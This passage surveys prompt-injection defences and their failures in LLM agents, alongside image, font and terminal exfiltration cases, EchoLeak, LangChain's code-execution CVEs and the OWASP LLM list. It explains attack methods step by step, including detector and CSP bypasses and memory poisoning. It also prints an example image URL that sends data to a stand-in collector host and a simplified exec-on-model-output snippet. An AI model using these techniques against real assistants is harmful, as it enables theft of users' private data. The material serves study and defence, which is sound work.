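The strongest test of both remedies is the October 2025 study by Nasr and colleagues. They tested the measures in this section mostly on AgentDojo, a simulated workplace where an agent uses tools to perform tasks and some of the material it reads contains planted instructions. They selected 80 pairs of a user's task and an attacker's goal. One language model proposed texts to plant, another scored the results, and a program kept the promising texts and prompted for improved versions, eight at a time.

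The table gives the attack success rates from the paper's main chart. "Old attacks" are fixed or weak attacks like those that earlier evaluations used.

| Defence | Method | Old attacks | Adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text | 28% | 99% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the request | 21% | 95% |
| Protect AI | Detector | 15% | 90% |
| PromptGuard | Detector | 26% | 94% |
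| PIGuard | Detector | 0% | 71% |
| Model Armor | Detector | 0% | 90% |

The figures for old attacks depend on the setting, since the paper's text also reports rates as low as 1% for the first two defences. The results for adaptive attacks are much clearer. Nasr and colleagues saw no measurable difference between the kinds of attack that worked with Spotlighting or sandwiching and the kinds that worked without them. One successful text presented the attacker's goal as a procedure the agent had to complete before doing what the user wanted. Repeating the user's request does not help against this, because the agent treats the procedure as a step in fulfilling that request.

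The texts that got past detectors were similarly bland. One was phrased as a company policy that required the agent to delete a certain file whenever it moved a meeting. A detector with no access to the company's real policies could hardly reject that sentence without also rejecting many legitimate ones. Combining several detectors did not stop the attacks either.

The automated search got past MELON's double run 76% of the time without information about how MELON worked. When the attacking model received a full description, it learned to add a condition telling the agent to ignore the planted instructions if it was only summarising. The agent then ignored them in the test run but followed them in the real one, and the success rate rose to 95%. Training a model to resist injected instructions did no better than screening. Meta SecAlign, which was trained this way, had held the standard AgentDojo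 attacks to a 2% success rate, but the adaptive search succeeded against it 96% of the time.

Human attackers confirmed these results in a contest with 40 challenges and $20,000 in prizes. They produced 265 successful attacks against Spotlighting, 178 against sandwiching and 123 against detectors on the strictest setting. They could watch the agent's reasoning and tool calls as it worked, and the automated attack on the detectors received each detector's confidence score. A stranger who emails somebody's assistant normally has neither kind of information. The study therefore shows that a well-informed attacker can break the defences, but it is weaker evidence about the risk from a stranger with one chance. It did not include Prompt Shields, so its results apply to that product only by analogy.

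Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors worth having against unsophisticated or opportunistic attacks. Red Hat calls detectors "at best a safety net" and compares them to web application firewalls, which block known attacks on websites whose owners can't properly secure the code.

### Evidence from 2026

Models have become much harder to attack since then. Fernando Irarrázaval challenged the public to email an assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6 and make it reveal a secret. Its only special protection seems to have been a short list of rules in its prompt, such as never to reveal credentials when an email asked for them. About 2,000 people made roughly 6,000 attempts, and all of them failed. Willison wrote about the challenge in June 2026, calling the result surprising and taking it as a sign that the AI companies' training was working. He still advised against building anything where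 a successful attack could do irreversible damage.

Detectors have also performed well in tests. Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, has an "auto mode" in which a separate classifier reviews each action before it runs. In July 2026, Trajectory Labs, a company commissioned by Anthropic, tested this mode on 72 indirect injection scenarios that Anthropic had not seen. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against the three Claude models in the test.

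As a rule of thumb, if *n* independent attempts all fail, the true success rate is probably below 3/*n* (with 95% confidence). That is about 0.4% for 720 attempts and 0.05% for 6,000 emails. But this limit applies only to the kinds of attack the testers tried. In August, Rehberger reported an attack on auto mode that he said worked 80% of the time with Claude Opus 5, one of the models in the July test. He got the agent to unpack an archive and run innocent-looking code, which silently loaded a malicious file from that archive. One reader objected that this was not really prompt injection, since the agent never obeyed a planted instruction. That is correct, and it is why a system could pass 720 tests for planted instructions and still be open to this attack.

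*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) examines this kind of gap systematically, using 90 cases built at Amazon. In each case, the attacker corrupts the agent's existing task instead of giving it a new one. In one, an agent must settle a customer's refund according to the shop's order record, which allows $899.99, but the customer's evidence gives $1,074.99. The attacker can demand the larger sum or make a false statement, for example that the displayed figure leaves out a repair allowance. The user's request always specifies which source to rely on, so a careful agent can get the answer right.

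The researchers ran 1,433 attacks against each combination of five models and several defences. The attackers had to plant their text in advance and could not watch the agent or revise the text, so the results complement those of the 2025 study. Without a defence, 17.0% of attacks succeeded. Spotlighting reduced this only to 15.6%, and sandwiching reduced it to 10.4%. Among the defences that left the agent able to do its ordinary work, the most effective was a detector from a system called DRIFT. It removes suspicious passages, and 6.6% of attacks succeeded against it.

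DRIFT's average combines types of attack with different success rates. Attacks that gave the agent a new goal, such as demanding the larger refund, succeeded 2.4% of the time, compared with 12.1% for those that misstated the current facts and 9.5% for those that misinterpreted a figure. In a closer analysis of two of the models, the detector completely removed 78% to 85% of the attacks that gave the agent a new goal, but only 26% to 34% of those that made false statements about facts or figures. Rewording the attacks to evade detection did not change the overall pattern.

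These percentages may not carry over to current models, since two of the five tested, Claude Sonnet 4 and 4.5, were more than a year old when the study appeared. The weakness arises because detectors look for instructions, while a false refund amount reads like any other evidence and need not contain one. Zhang and colleagues suggest that a screening system should check whether the source of a claim has the authority to settle the matter, and that the agent's software should accept important values, such as refund amounts, only from a source that does. The second check can run outside the model, where the customer's wording does not affect it.

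## Data theft through images and links in chatbot answers

When a chatbot's answer includes an image, the program that displays the answer fetches the image from whatever address the model wrote. An attacker who controls the model's output can put private data into that address and collect it when the program requests the image. This is one of the most common flaws in LLM products. The program can prevent the theft by blocking requests to unknown hosts, which works even if the attacker's text fools the model because the block is outside the model. Security testers and vendors had identified both the flaw and the remedy by mid-2023, but new products still had the flaw in 2026.

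### How an image carries data out

Chatbots usually format their answers in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and images. An image in Markdown looks like this:

```
![logo](https://collector.example/logo.png?note=meeting-moved-to-Friday)
```

To get the picture, the browser requests the whole address, including the text after the question mark. Whoever runs the server can read that text in its log, whether or not a picture exists. Some email senders use the same method. Second Thoughts' *Anatomy of a Hack* explains that an email can include an image whose address identifies the recipient, so a request for that image shows that the recipient opened the message.

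An attacker can steal a chatbot user's data through indirect prompt injection, by planting instructions in content the model reads. The instructions make the model include an image in its answer whose address points to the attacker's server and ends in a summary of the conversation. The user's browser immediately requests the image, which sends the summary to the attacker. A link would send it only if the user clicked.

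Prompt injection has no reliable fix. The rest of the attack relies on an ordinary web flaw, in which the application displays untrusted text without restricting what that text can load. OWASP's list of LLM risks covers this flaw under output handling. *When your AI Assistant has an evil twin*, a write-up by the security firm WithSecure, recommends blocking every address the model writes or checking it against a list of permitted domains. It also recommends a Content Security Policy (CSP), a list sent with a website's pages that tells the browser which hosts may supply images, fonts and other material. Because the browser enforces the list, it can stop the data from being sent even when an attacker fully controls the model.

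### The first reports

Roman Samoilenko found the flaw in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023, and Rehberger found it independently a few days later. Samoilenko's attack, which Willison (2023) called ingenious, began on a website that secretly added instructions to any text the user copied. If the user pasted the text into ChatGPT, the answer included a single-pixel image that leaked the chat.

Rehberger's *ChatGPT Plugins* described an attack that required no pasting, because the instructions could sit in anything retrieved by a plugin, an add-on that connected ChatGPT to another service. In May, he used one plugin to read a hostile page, a second to fetch the user's latest email, and the first again to send the email's contents away. In *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, Willison called it the first working demonstration he had seen of such a theft through plugins.

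The table shows how three vendors handled Rehberger's reports, according to his blog, Embrace The Red.

| Product | Reported | First response | Fix | What remained open |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | Microsoft acknowledged the problem | By 15 June 2023, a CSP allowed images from only a few hosts | Nothing that Rehberger's retest found |
| ChatGPT | 9 April 2023 | OpenAI called it a feature and planned no change | In December 2023, the web app began checking image addresses | Small leaks, and the iOS app |
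| Claude | 12 July 2023 | Anthropic confirmed it on 18 July | By 26 July 2023, users had to click "Show Image" | Leaks after a click, and the iOS app |

Microsoft's fix was the strictest of the three. Text that Rehberger had planted in a web page made Bing Chat, after two turns of conversation, leak a short summary and any passwords on the page. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* reports that the new policy listed four Bing hosts and that his earlier attacks stopped working.

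Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions* argued that OpenAI could have fixed the flaw easily in April, but that the delay had made a fix harder because more and more plugins had come to rely on ChatGPT loading images from anywhere. Rehberger kept producing demonstrations, and SecurityWeek covered one of them, a custom version of ChatGPT that stole its user's data. OpenAI's first fix appeared the day after he showed this version live to a consenting victim, though nothing indicates that the demonstration prompted the fix.

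The fix was partial. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* explains that the web app now had an OpenAI server check whether each image address was safe. The server rejected an image address containing an email address but accepted some very short image addresses. Rehberger prepared one image for each letter and digit, and the server accepted 9 of the 36, so an attack could still leak data one request at a time. Nine usable addresses can encode any six-digit code in seven requests, since 9⁷ is more than a million, provided all the requests arrive in order. He suggested limiting the number of images in an answer, which would slow such leaks.

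Anthropic acted within two weeks, but Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* describes the "Show Image" button as imperfect because it leaves the decision to the user. Anthropic's iOS app still loaded images automatically until December 2024, when Rehberger announced another fix (Willison, 2024).

Google's chatbot Bard already had a CSP, which allowed images from any address ending in google.com. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* shows how Rehberger got past it with Google Apps Script, a service that lets anyone run small programs at a Google address. An attacker could collect data at such an address even though the browser enforced the policy correctly.

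### Talks and the Month of AI Bugs

Rehberger's talks show how the advice developed. In his 2023 HITCON slides, he listed instructing the model to resist attacks among the defences, but labelled it "Begging defense". In his slides for the Chaos Communication Congress that December, he dropped that item and added that a CSP can mitigate image attacks. In both sets of slides, he also gave developers the more general rule not to trust the model's output.

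In August 2025, he published the Month of AI Bugs, a series of nearly daily posts about flaws in AI products, mostly coding agents. *Month of bugs* lists campaigns in the same format against Apple and PHP in 2007. Embrace The Red's *The Month of AI Bugs* (2025) said one aim was to expose unresponsive vendors and encourage timely action. Embrace The Red's *Wrap Up* lists 29 posts covering more than a dozen products, and 12 of the titles mention leaked data or secrets.

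The series repeated much the same test on one vendor's product after another. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* reports that Rehberger reused an old demonstration on the coding agent Amp Code and it "happened to just work". Microsoft had fixed a similar flaw in GitHub Copilot the year before. Rehberger also retested products after repairs. Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio* describes a leak through images that he found in that product after an earlier report, when it still had no CSP.

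Rehberger's posts reached developers through newsletters such as O'Reilly's (2025) and through Willison's *The Summer of Johann*, which drew on them for a general warning about broad lists of permitted domains. Academic researchers also used the posts, and four of the six real attacks that Chang and colleagues analysed in 2026 came from Rehberger's blog.

Publicity could also change a vendor's decision. On 25 October 2025, Rehberger told Anthropic that Claude could leak a user's data through Anthropic's own file-upload interface. According to Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, Anthropic closed the report an hour later as a model safety issue outside the scope of its programme. After a public discussion, Anthropic accepted the report as a valid security flaw on 30 October, according to eSecurity Planet's *Hackers Turn Claude AI Into Data Thief With New Attack*.

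However, the series mostly describes attacks that worked, so readers can't tell how many products would have passed the same tests. It also doesn't give success rates that would allow fair comparisons between products. Rehberger had collected earlier cases in a paper, *Trust No AI* (2024), which is easier to cite but predates his 2025 tests.

### EchoLeak

EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, is the best test of the standard advice because Microsoft had followed much of it. Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their email, files and chats. Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, found that an outsider could steal data from these sources by sending one email. Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, Microsoft finished its patch in May, and Aim Labs published its findings on 11 June, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*.

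Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2025-32711, at 9.3 on the standard ten-point severity scale. The US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, as *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) notes. Microsoft knew of no attack on customers.

The attacker's email first had to turn up in Copilot's search. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes a long email divided into supposed guides to staff onboarding, leave and other common topics, with the same instructions under each heading. Some part of the email was therefore likely to match whichever topic the employee asked about. The instructions told Copilot to take the most sensitive information it could see and put it into an image address.

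Several protections stood in the way:

- **A detector for prompt injection.** The researchers got past it by wording the instructions as if for the human recipient, with no mention of AI or Copilot.
- **A filter that removed external links and images.** Markdown also allows a writer to give the address separately, rather like a footnote, and the filter did not recognise that form.
- **A CSP.** It blocked the attacker's server, but its nearly 30 entries included all of Microsoft Teams. One Teams address would fetch any other address on request, so the browser contacted Microsoft, and Microsoft's server passed the data to the attacker.
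- **References to sources.** Copilot normally names the material behind an answer, which might have exposed the email. The email told its "recipient" never to mention it, for compliance reasons.

*EchoLeak* (2025), an academic case study, points out that Copilot also had no tool for sending email. The browser's image request could still send data to an outsider, but nobody had listed it among Copilot's tools, so by the usual reading of least privilege, Copilot had no way to do this.

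The detector failed as critics of detectors had predicted. The filter had an ordinary programming gap, which Microsoft could close. The CSP did restrict the attack. The researchers had to search Microsoft's services for a way around it, and the first one they found, in SharePoint, required the victim to accept an invitation. A shorter list of allowed hosts, with none that forwards requests, would have blocked the automatic leak, though a user could still have clicked a link. Bard's policy had failed for much the same reason in 2023.

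Ravia recommends Aim's own product, a guardrail that looks for outside emails trying to reach internal data. It may catch more attacks than Microsoft's detector did, but the recommendation is commercial, and unlike a strict list of hosts, the guardrail has to recognise an attack to stop it. Ravia's claim that this was the first "zero-click" AI flaw also needs some qualification, because Rehberger's attack on Bing Chat in 2023 had needed no click either. Willison (2025) called the flaw an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. It was new in that the victim did not have to open the attacker's material, only ask Copilot a question about work.

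### Fonts, memory and terminals

A few months after the EchoLeak patch, Rehberger found another way to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot, which he presented at DEF CON Singapore in 2026. Copilot had gained a window for previewing web pages it wrote. The window removed image tags, but web pages can also load fonts, and Copilot's policy was looser for fonts than for images. Rehberger found this by asking Copilot to look for ways to load outside material. The preview normally opened only when the user clicked, so the planted instructions told Copilot to open it.

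In one of his demonstrations, a user opens a shared Word document and types "hi there". Copilot searches the mailbox for a particular email and writes the email's contents into a font address, which the preview then requests. According to Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, he reported the flaw on 16 October 2025, Microsoft reproduced it on 12 November, and the fix was complete on 5 March 2026. The CSP also differed between Word, Excel and other places where Copilot appeared, so testing one revealed little about the others.

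He then combined the leak with Copilot's long-term memory. A harmless-looking biography of Einstein contained instructions for Copilot to end its summary by asking whether it had been helpful. When the user answered yes or no, Copilot saved a new "preference" to memory. In later conversations, Copilot would leak any password the user pasted by including it in the font address. Microsoft reported the memory flaw as fixed in December 2025, but its April 2026 documentation still stated that memory changes left no entries in the audit log, which would make such an attack hard to investigate.

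Chang and colleagues use this case to show a gap in defences that restrict untrusted sources. Once an instruction from a stranger's document is in memory, the agent may later treat it as trusted guidance, and deleting the document does not remove it.

A chatbot's memory of a user is also worth stealing. In July 2026, *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) showed that Claude could leak what it had stored about a user through its tool for reading web pages. Willison had admired that tool's protections against this kind of theft. In a conversation that looked innocent, Claude disclosed Paul's name, employer and answers to security questions.

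The terminal, the text window where programmers type commands, had the same problem as the browser. Terminals respond to escape codes, invisible characters that change colours or move the cursor. After Leon Derczynski described how LLMs can produce these codes, Rehberger tested what an attacker could do with them. One code made Apple's Terminal look up an internet address. An attacker can run the name server that receives the lookup, so the name being looked up can carry data to them, just as an image address can.

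Chang and colleagues summarise a case from July 2026 in which someone asks a command-line assistant about one customer in a spreadsheet. An instruction planted in a cell makes the model write other customers' details into an escape code, and Terminal sends them out. The model only writes text, so a control that inspects tool calls would not detect the theft.

Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* had already recommended in 2024 that a program print escape codes as visible characters unless it needs them. David Leadbeater had described the Terminal flaw at DEF CON in 2023, without discussing LLMs. Apple has since fixed it, according to Security Arsenal's *macOS Terminal ANSI Escape Code DNS Exfiltration* (2026), a security vendor's post from July.

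### Why the flaw kept returning

The main reason is that the fix belongs in the program that displays the answer, and each product may have several such programs. A fix to Claude's website did not protect its iOS app, which leaked data for another 17 months. In August 2026, Cyber Security News' *OpenAI Codex Desktop App for macOS Vulnerability* (2026) reported that OpenAI's desktop app for its coding agent loaded remote images automatically. OpenAI had first received a report of this behaviour in ChatGPT more than three years earlier.

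Vendors also tended to treat the reports as complaints about the model. OpenAI called image loading a feature, and Anthropic initially filed the upload flaw under model safety. Google was working on a fix for data theft through prompt injection in its Antigravity coding tool, but it listed the problem as a known issue, which Willison noted made reports ineligible for a reward. Reports classified this way go to people who train models, although a developer could often close the leak by changing a few lines of the display program.

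Another explanation, from Rehberger and quoted by Willison in December 2025, is that companies "confuse the absence of a successful attack with the presence of robust security". This may explain why they loosened controls as models improved, but not OpenAI's refusal in April 2023, when ChatGPT's plugins were too new to have a reassuring record.

The most popular form of the advice, "block unknown image hosts", was also too narrow. It covers only one route and assumes that known hosts are harmless, but attackers found other routes and ways to exploit known hosts. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without approval, and Willison described how images in those emails leaked data when the user opened them. A better rule is that no program should automatically contact an address that a model wrote after reading untrusted text. A chatbot that only answers questions would lose little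 more than some images under this rule.

An agent that browses the web cannot follow that rule, because browsing requires it to request web addresses. An attack called ShadowLeak used an email with hidden instructions to make ChatGPT's Deep Research agent search the user's inbox and visit an address containing what it found. *Compositional Threat Analysis* reports that the attack succeeded in every repeated test. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so the user's browser and the employer's monitoring software might not have detected it.

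Google and OpenAI now use their search indexes to limit which addresses their assistants may open without asking the user. An address that the model has created to hold someone's password will not be in the index. Rehberger thinks Microsoft should adopt the same check because it prevents large thefts, though an attacker can still leak small amounts of data by choosing among addresses that already exist.

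## LangChain and the security documentation of agent frameworks

The program that displays a chatbot's answer may fetch any image address the model writes. Some early LLM applications went much further and ran the model's output as code. LangChain, an open-source framework, gave developers ready-made components for doing this.

### What a framework supplies

A framework is a library of code that many applications need. In July 2023, LangChain (2023) offered prompt templates, memory, connections to other software, agents, and "chains", which are fixed sequences of calls to a model or another program. A developer could install it with one command, then import a finished chain and connect it to a model.

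Each component of an agent framework includes a security decision, such as whether model-written code runs in a sandbox or whether a person must approve a payment. A developer who keeps the default leaves that decision to the framework's designers, perhaps without noticing. Example code has a similar effect because developers copy it, whereas a written warning affects only those who read it.

The problem appears to have gone beyond one framework. *A Survey on Large Language Model (LLM) Security and Privacy* (2023) cites researchers who found 13 vulnerabilities in six frameworks, including 12 that let an attacker run code. The researchers also tested 51 applications and found 17 vulnerable, including 16 in which an attacker could use prompt injection to run code on the server.

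### How a question became running code

LangChain's `llm_math` chain answered maths questions by having the model write a program to calculate the answer. In simplified form, it worked like this:

```
code = model("Write Python code that answers: " + question)
exec(code)
```

The Python function `exec` runs text as a program. If a user asked for the sum of the first six Fibonacci numbers, the model wrote a few lines of code to add them, and the chain ran the code and returned the result. Only the wording of the prompt limited the code to arithmetic. NVIDIA's *Securing LLM Systems Against Prompt Injection* describes a test by the company's AI red team, which attacks systems to find flaws. The team gave the chain some code with an instruction to repeat it. The model repeated the code, and the chain ran it and displayed the contents of a file.

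The team found the same pattern in two other chains. One sent requests to web services, and an attacker could redirect them to a different address. The other, `SQLDatabaseChain`, turned questions into database commands and ran them, and it would also run an attacker's command. Parameterised queries could not have prevented this, because they protect values inside a fixed command, and here the model wrote the whole command.

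The first public report of the maths flaw appeared on 30 January 2023 in LangChain's issue tracker on GitHub. Two more reports followed in February. At the end of March, NVIDIA requested a CVE number because the flaw was severe and LangChain had not acted quickly. MITRE's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023) appeared on 5 April. INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists the flaw's severity as 9.8 out of 10 in its own entry, *CVE-2023-29374* (2023).

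LangChain blocked that attack in version 0.0.141 by replacing `exec` with numexpr, a library that evaluates numerical expressions. But OSV's *CVE-2023-39631* (2023), published on 1 September, reported that an attacker could run code through numexpr as well, so LangChain needed another patch.

GitLab's *CVE-2023-36258* (2023) recorded a similar flaw on 3 July in `PALChain`, which solved word problems by writing Python. Three days later, GitLab's *CVE-2023-36189* (2023) recorded a flaw in `SQLDatabaseChain`. `SQLDatabaseChain` received a second CVE number in October, according to Snyk's *SQL Injection Affecting langchain package, versions [,0.0.276)* (2023), so the CVE count overstates the number of separate problems.

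### Moving the code

On 21 July 2023, LangChain's founder, Harrison Chase, committed a change titled "remove CVEs". It copied the components with CVE records, with "zero changes to functionality", into what became a separate package, `langchain_experimental`. LangChain released the package the next day and gave developers a week before removing the originals. The table shows this and the later changes.

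| Date | Change | What developers could still do |
|---|---|---|
| 21–22 July 2023 | Maintainers copied components with CVE records into `langchain_experimental` | Use either copy, with the same behaviour |
| 16 October 2023 | The documentation gained a security page about limiting permissions | Build an application without opening the page |
| 27 October 2023 | Maintainers deprecated the Python tools and data-frame agents in the main package | Import them from `langchain_experimental` |
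| By 16 June 2024 | Data-frame agents and `PALChain` required `allow_dangerous_code=True` | Set the flag and run them without a sandbox |

In its announcement, LangChain said it wanted to make the main package more robust while continuing to experiment elsewhere. The move improved the default, since new developers who installed only the main package would no longer get these chains. It did much less for people who already used them. *Create_python_agent has been moved to langchain experimental*, a post on the forum of the course provider DeepLearning.AI, quotes the error that appeared when an old import stopped working. The error included the code's new location, and the post included instructions for installing the extra package. Anyone who followed these instructions had the same risk as before.

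The US National Vulnerability Database recommended upgrading LangChain to fix CVE-2023-39659, a flaw in its data-frame agent, which answers questions about tables by writing and running Python. Consumer Reports, an American product-testing organisation, was using this agent to build a way to query its ratings in plain English. Include Security, a firm that Consumer Reports had hired, found that the maintainers had only moved the code. A published attack still worked with the latest version, according to Consumer Reports' *Who's Verifying the Verifier*. Include Security also found three discussions about safer ways to run the code, but a bot had closed all three without a solution. Consumer Reports began looking for an alternative.

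Yurtsev's *Deprecate PythonRepl tools and Pandas/Xorbits/Spark DataFrame/Python/CSV agents (CVE-2023-39659)* (2023) removed this agent from the main package. LangChain explained that the code was safe only in an appropriate sandbox and kept it available in the experimental package. The vulnerability databases recorded only a version number, omitting both the sandbox requirement and the code's continued availability.

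The maintainers also tried to filter dangerous code in `PALChain`, but the filter did not block imports, which load other Python modules. GitLab's *CVE-2023-44467* (2023) recorded the bypass on 9 October. On 5 October, the project had added another maths chain, which passed text to a function that uses Python's `eval`, which is similar to `exec`. Wiz's *CVE-2024-46946* lists this chain as another way to run arbitrary code.

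### The advice on permissions

LangChain's security page appeared more than eight months after the first public report. In *Add security.md*, Yurtsev (2023) told developers to grant only the access an application needs, to consider read-only credentials and sandboxes, and to combine several defences. If a model's credentials allow it to delete data, developers should assume it might.

This advice is sound and does not depend on recognising an attack. But all three of the page's example scenarios begin with a user asking an agent to do something harmful. None involves instructions hidden in a document the agent reads, although Greshake and colleagues had described that attack in February. A developer whose users were trusted colleagues might therefore have thought the examples did not apply. LangChain's *Security policy* still has the same three scenarios, but its list of precautions now includes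 using a proxy to control outside requests, which could help prevent data theft.

NVIDIA's advice covered hidden instructions more directly. The company recommended giving each call to an outside service only the privileges of the least trusted party whose text had contributed to the prompt. David C later took much the same rule from an exchange on X. The rule is harder to apply than a read-only password because the application has to track where every piece of text came from.

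### Who is responsible

The maintainers left the sandbox to developers for a technical reason. In a documentation change for `PALChain`, LangChain explained that its own protections could not replace a proper sandbox, which has to be outside the Python process where the package runs. Whoever deploys the code must therefore set up the sandbox. The failed filters support this argument. Langroid, another framework, also added a filter for model-written expressions, and GitLab describes how an attacker could bypass it.

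Weak protections can also mislead users. *Harness Engineering* (2026), a study of the source code of eleven coding agents, found that one of them, Pi, has no built-in sandbox by design. According to Pi's documentation, a partial sandbox "would be easy to misunderstand as a security boundary".

LangChain applied the same reasoning to its bug bounty, which pays people who report flaws. Its *Security Policy* excluded tools and the experimental package from the bounty, and stated that developers "are responsible for the security of their tools". In Yurtsev and Friis's *Remove Python REPL from community*, the maintainers moved a tool for running Python out of the community package, but insisted that it was "not a bug in the code or an actual security risk". They moved it to satisfy security policies based on a simple search for `exec`.

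*Impact of remote-code execution vulnerability in LangChain* (2023), a developer's blog post from 10 July, blamed the whole group of flaws on "an underlying design issue" in the framework. It also noted that a model could write destructive code by mistake, without any attacker. Exploit Intel's *CVE-2024-38459* (2024) shows that the missing opt-in step later received its own CVE number, categorized as incorrect default permissions, and lists no known exploitation.

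The maintainers were right that a tool for running Python has to run Python, and that a library cannot build the developer's sandbox. But when the developer has done nothing about security, a component can refuse to start until they make an explicit choice. This check takes only a few lines of code, and LangChain added one about 16 months after the first public report. The argument for developer responsibility is also weaker for a maths chain than for a tool called "Python REPL", because programmers can tell from the latter's name that it runs code.

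Yurtsev's *Force users to opt-in into code that relies on the python repl* introduced the opt-in check, which raises an error that explains the danger and names the flag that turns the component on. This works only if the person who sets the flag understands the deployment. Langflow, a tool for building agents from connected components, set the flag to `True` in its own code for analysing tables and gave users no way to turn it off. Its developers had thus accepted the risk on behalf of users who may never have seen LangChain's warning. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-376* (2026), an attacker could take over a Langflow server through prompt injection. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-27966* lists version 1.8.0 as the fix.

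LangChain has since moved somewhat towards its critics. It says its current reporting programme includes vulnerabilities that affect "a project's default behavior" and common configurations. However, LangChain's *Python REPL integration* page still shows developers how to give an agent a Python tool, using an example without a sandbox. The page warns that the tool can delete files and make network requests, and that the experimental package is no longer maintained.

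### Whether later frameworks improved

In later advice based on its assessments of AI systems, NVIDIA still called running a model's output as code with `exec` or `eval` "one of the most serious and recurring issues". *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (2026) examined 295 GitHub security advisories related to LLM packages. Code injection was the most frequent weakness, with 24 occurrences, followed by command injection and unsafe loading of stored data, with 22 each. The study found no new kind of implementation weakness specific to LLMs. The counts cover only published advisories, so they don't show what share of frameworks or applications is vulnerable.

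LangChain's main package also had such a flaw. It used a key called `lc` to mark stored objects, but did not properly escape that key in data from users. Microsoft explains that an attacker could use this to make the framework rebuild a malicious object. The flaw had an ordinary fix, unlike the confusion of instructions and data inside a model, and LangChain released patched versions.

An agent can also misuse a tool it is supposed to have, and sandboxing code does not prevent this. A framework can limit which tools the model may request, but an agent that handles refunds needs a refund tool, so something must also check each request, including the amount and the account that will receive the money. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) uses the term capability gate for the limit on tools and per-call authorisation for the check on each request.

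Mellafe Zuvic, an independent researcher, read fixed versions of the public source code of three projects: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, the rival framework LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to a payment company. Mellafe Zuvic looked for a default check that compared the values in a model's request with a policy before the tool ran and blocked any request that violated it. All three projects had capability gates, but none had this check.

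LlamaIndex looks up the tool the model has named and, if it exists, calls it with the values the model supplied. A schema can specify the form of these values, such as text for an account number, but it cannot be used to check whether the account belongs to an attacker. LangChain works in much the same way. Developers can add human approval to either framework, but neither requires it. Stripe's toolkit lets developers restrict the available actions and the access key's permissions, then passes on the amounts and customers the model has chosen.

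To demonstrate the gap, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed model output that called for changing a merchant's payout account to an attacker's. LangChain made the change on a simulated payment system, and LlamaIndex did the same in a companion test. Fixing the output made sense because the test was about what the framework does after an attack has already fooled the model.

A separate test of 27 models measured how often they attempted unauthorised actions when a planted instruction seemed to be part of the user's task. The average was 60% for 12 cheaper models and 19% for 15 flagship models. The test environment blocked the actions, so these rates count only attempts, and all the scenarios came from one author.

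Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, is a program that runs between the model and the tools. It blocks any tool that the operator has not listed, any restricted value outside an approved set, and any payment above a ceiling. It also requires a key that prevents repeated payments, and it refuses the call if an error occurs. No language model helps make the decision, and the policy must never come from a model's output.

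In the tests, ScopeGate blocked all 48 prepared attempts to evade it. It also blocked all 29 unauthorised requests from an adaptive attacker, a model that saw the reason for each refusal and had 40 rounds to find a way through. All ten legitimate requests passed. Mellafe Zuvic designed both the control and the tests, and an earlier version of ScopeGate let through a payment whose amount was "not a number", a special value that passed a careless comparison. The main result is still easy to believe, because persuasive wording can't add an attacker's account to a list the model can't edit.

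Such a list helps only when the operator knows the permitted values in advance. An email assistant that must answer strangers cannot have a complete list of approved recipients. A payment ceiling would also miss an inflated refund that stays below it, as in the case from Zhang and colleagues. Catching that requires checking the amount against the order record.

*Delegation Without Trust* (September 2026) reached a similar conclusion about four widely used frameworks, including CrewAI, AutoGen and the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting LLM applications to tools. Three provided no authorisation by default, and MCP provided partial authorisation. The study examined the code of CrewAI and AutoGen and the written specification of MCP, so it shows what their designs provide, not how often deployed applications lack these checks. The maintainers of the other three frameworks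 do not claim to provide authorisation systems, and cannot know which accounts a shop has approved. But they could prevent a payment tool from running until the developer supplies a policy, much as LangChain eventually required developers to set a flag before running Python.

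## The OWASP Top 10 for LLM applications

Documentation like LangChain's covers one product. For general advice on LLM security, developers could turn to the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications, a ranked list of risks that volunteers first published in 2023 and have revised several times. Its advice on prompt injection has improved, moving from filtering the attacker's text towards limiting what a model can do once an injection succeeds. Its ranking is harder to trust. OWASP first compared its members' votes with a large set of recorded incidents in August 2026. Prompt injection came first in the vote but would not have made the top ten on incidents alone, and OWASP's explanation for the gap is only one of several that fit the results.

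### A first draft by ChatGPT

Steve Wilson started the list in spring 2023, when he was chief product officer of the software security company Contrast Security. In *The OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications*, a chapter of his O'Reilly book on LLM security, Wilson recalls finding very little organised research on the subject. He collected some papers and blog posts and had ChatGPT summarise them. Then he gave ChatGPT a few examples from OWASP's list of web application risks and asked it to draft a similar list for LLMs.

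Wilson sent the draft to Jeff Williams, who had written the first OWASP Top 10 and was Contrast Security's chief technology officer, without telling him that ChatGPT had written most of it. Williams encouraged him, but Wilson had only wanted to know whether the list looked novel and worth pursuing, not whether it was accurate. Infosecurity Magazine's *What the OWASP Top 10 for LLMs Means* reports that Wilson produced the draft, version 0.1, alone over a weekend.

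OWASP (2023) announced the project on 23 May and gave newcomers a reading list of 12 items, mostly blog posts and news articles. The list included Selvi's post for NCC Group and two by Rehberger. Wilson planned to finish in eight weeks. In Security Boulevard's *OWASP Top 10 for LLMs* (2023), he explained that software teams had so little guidance that "the most important thing is to get something out".

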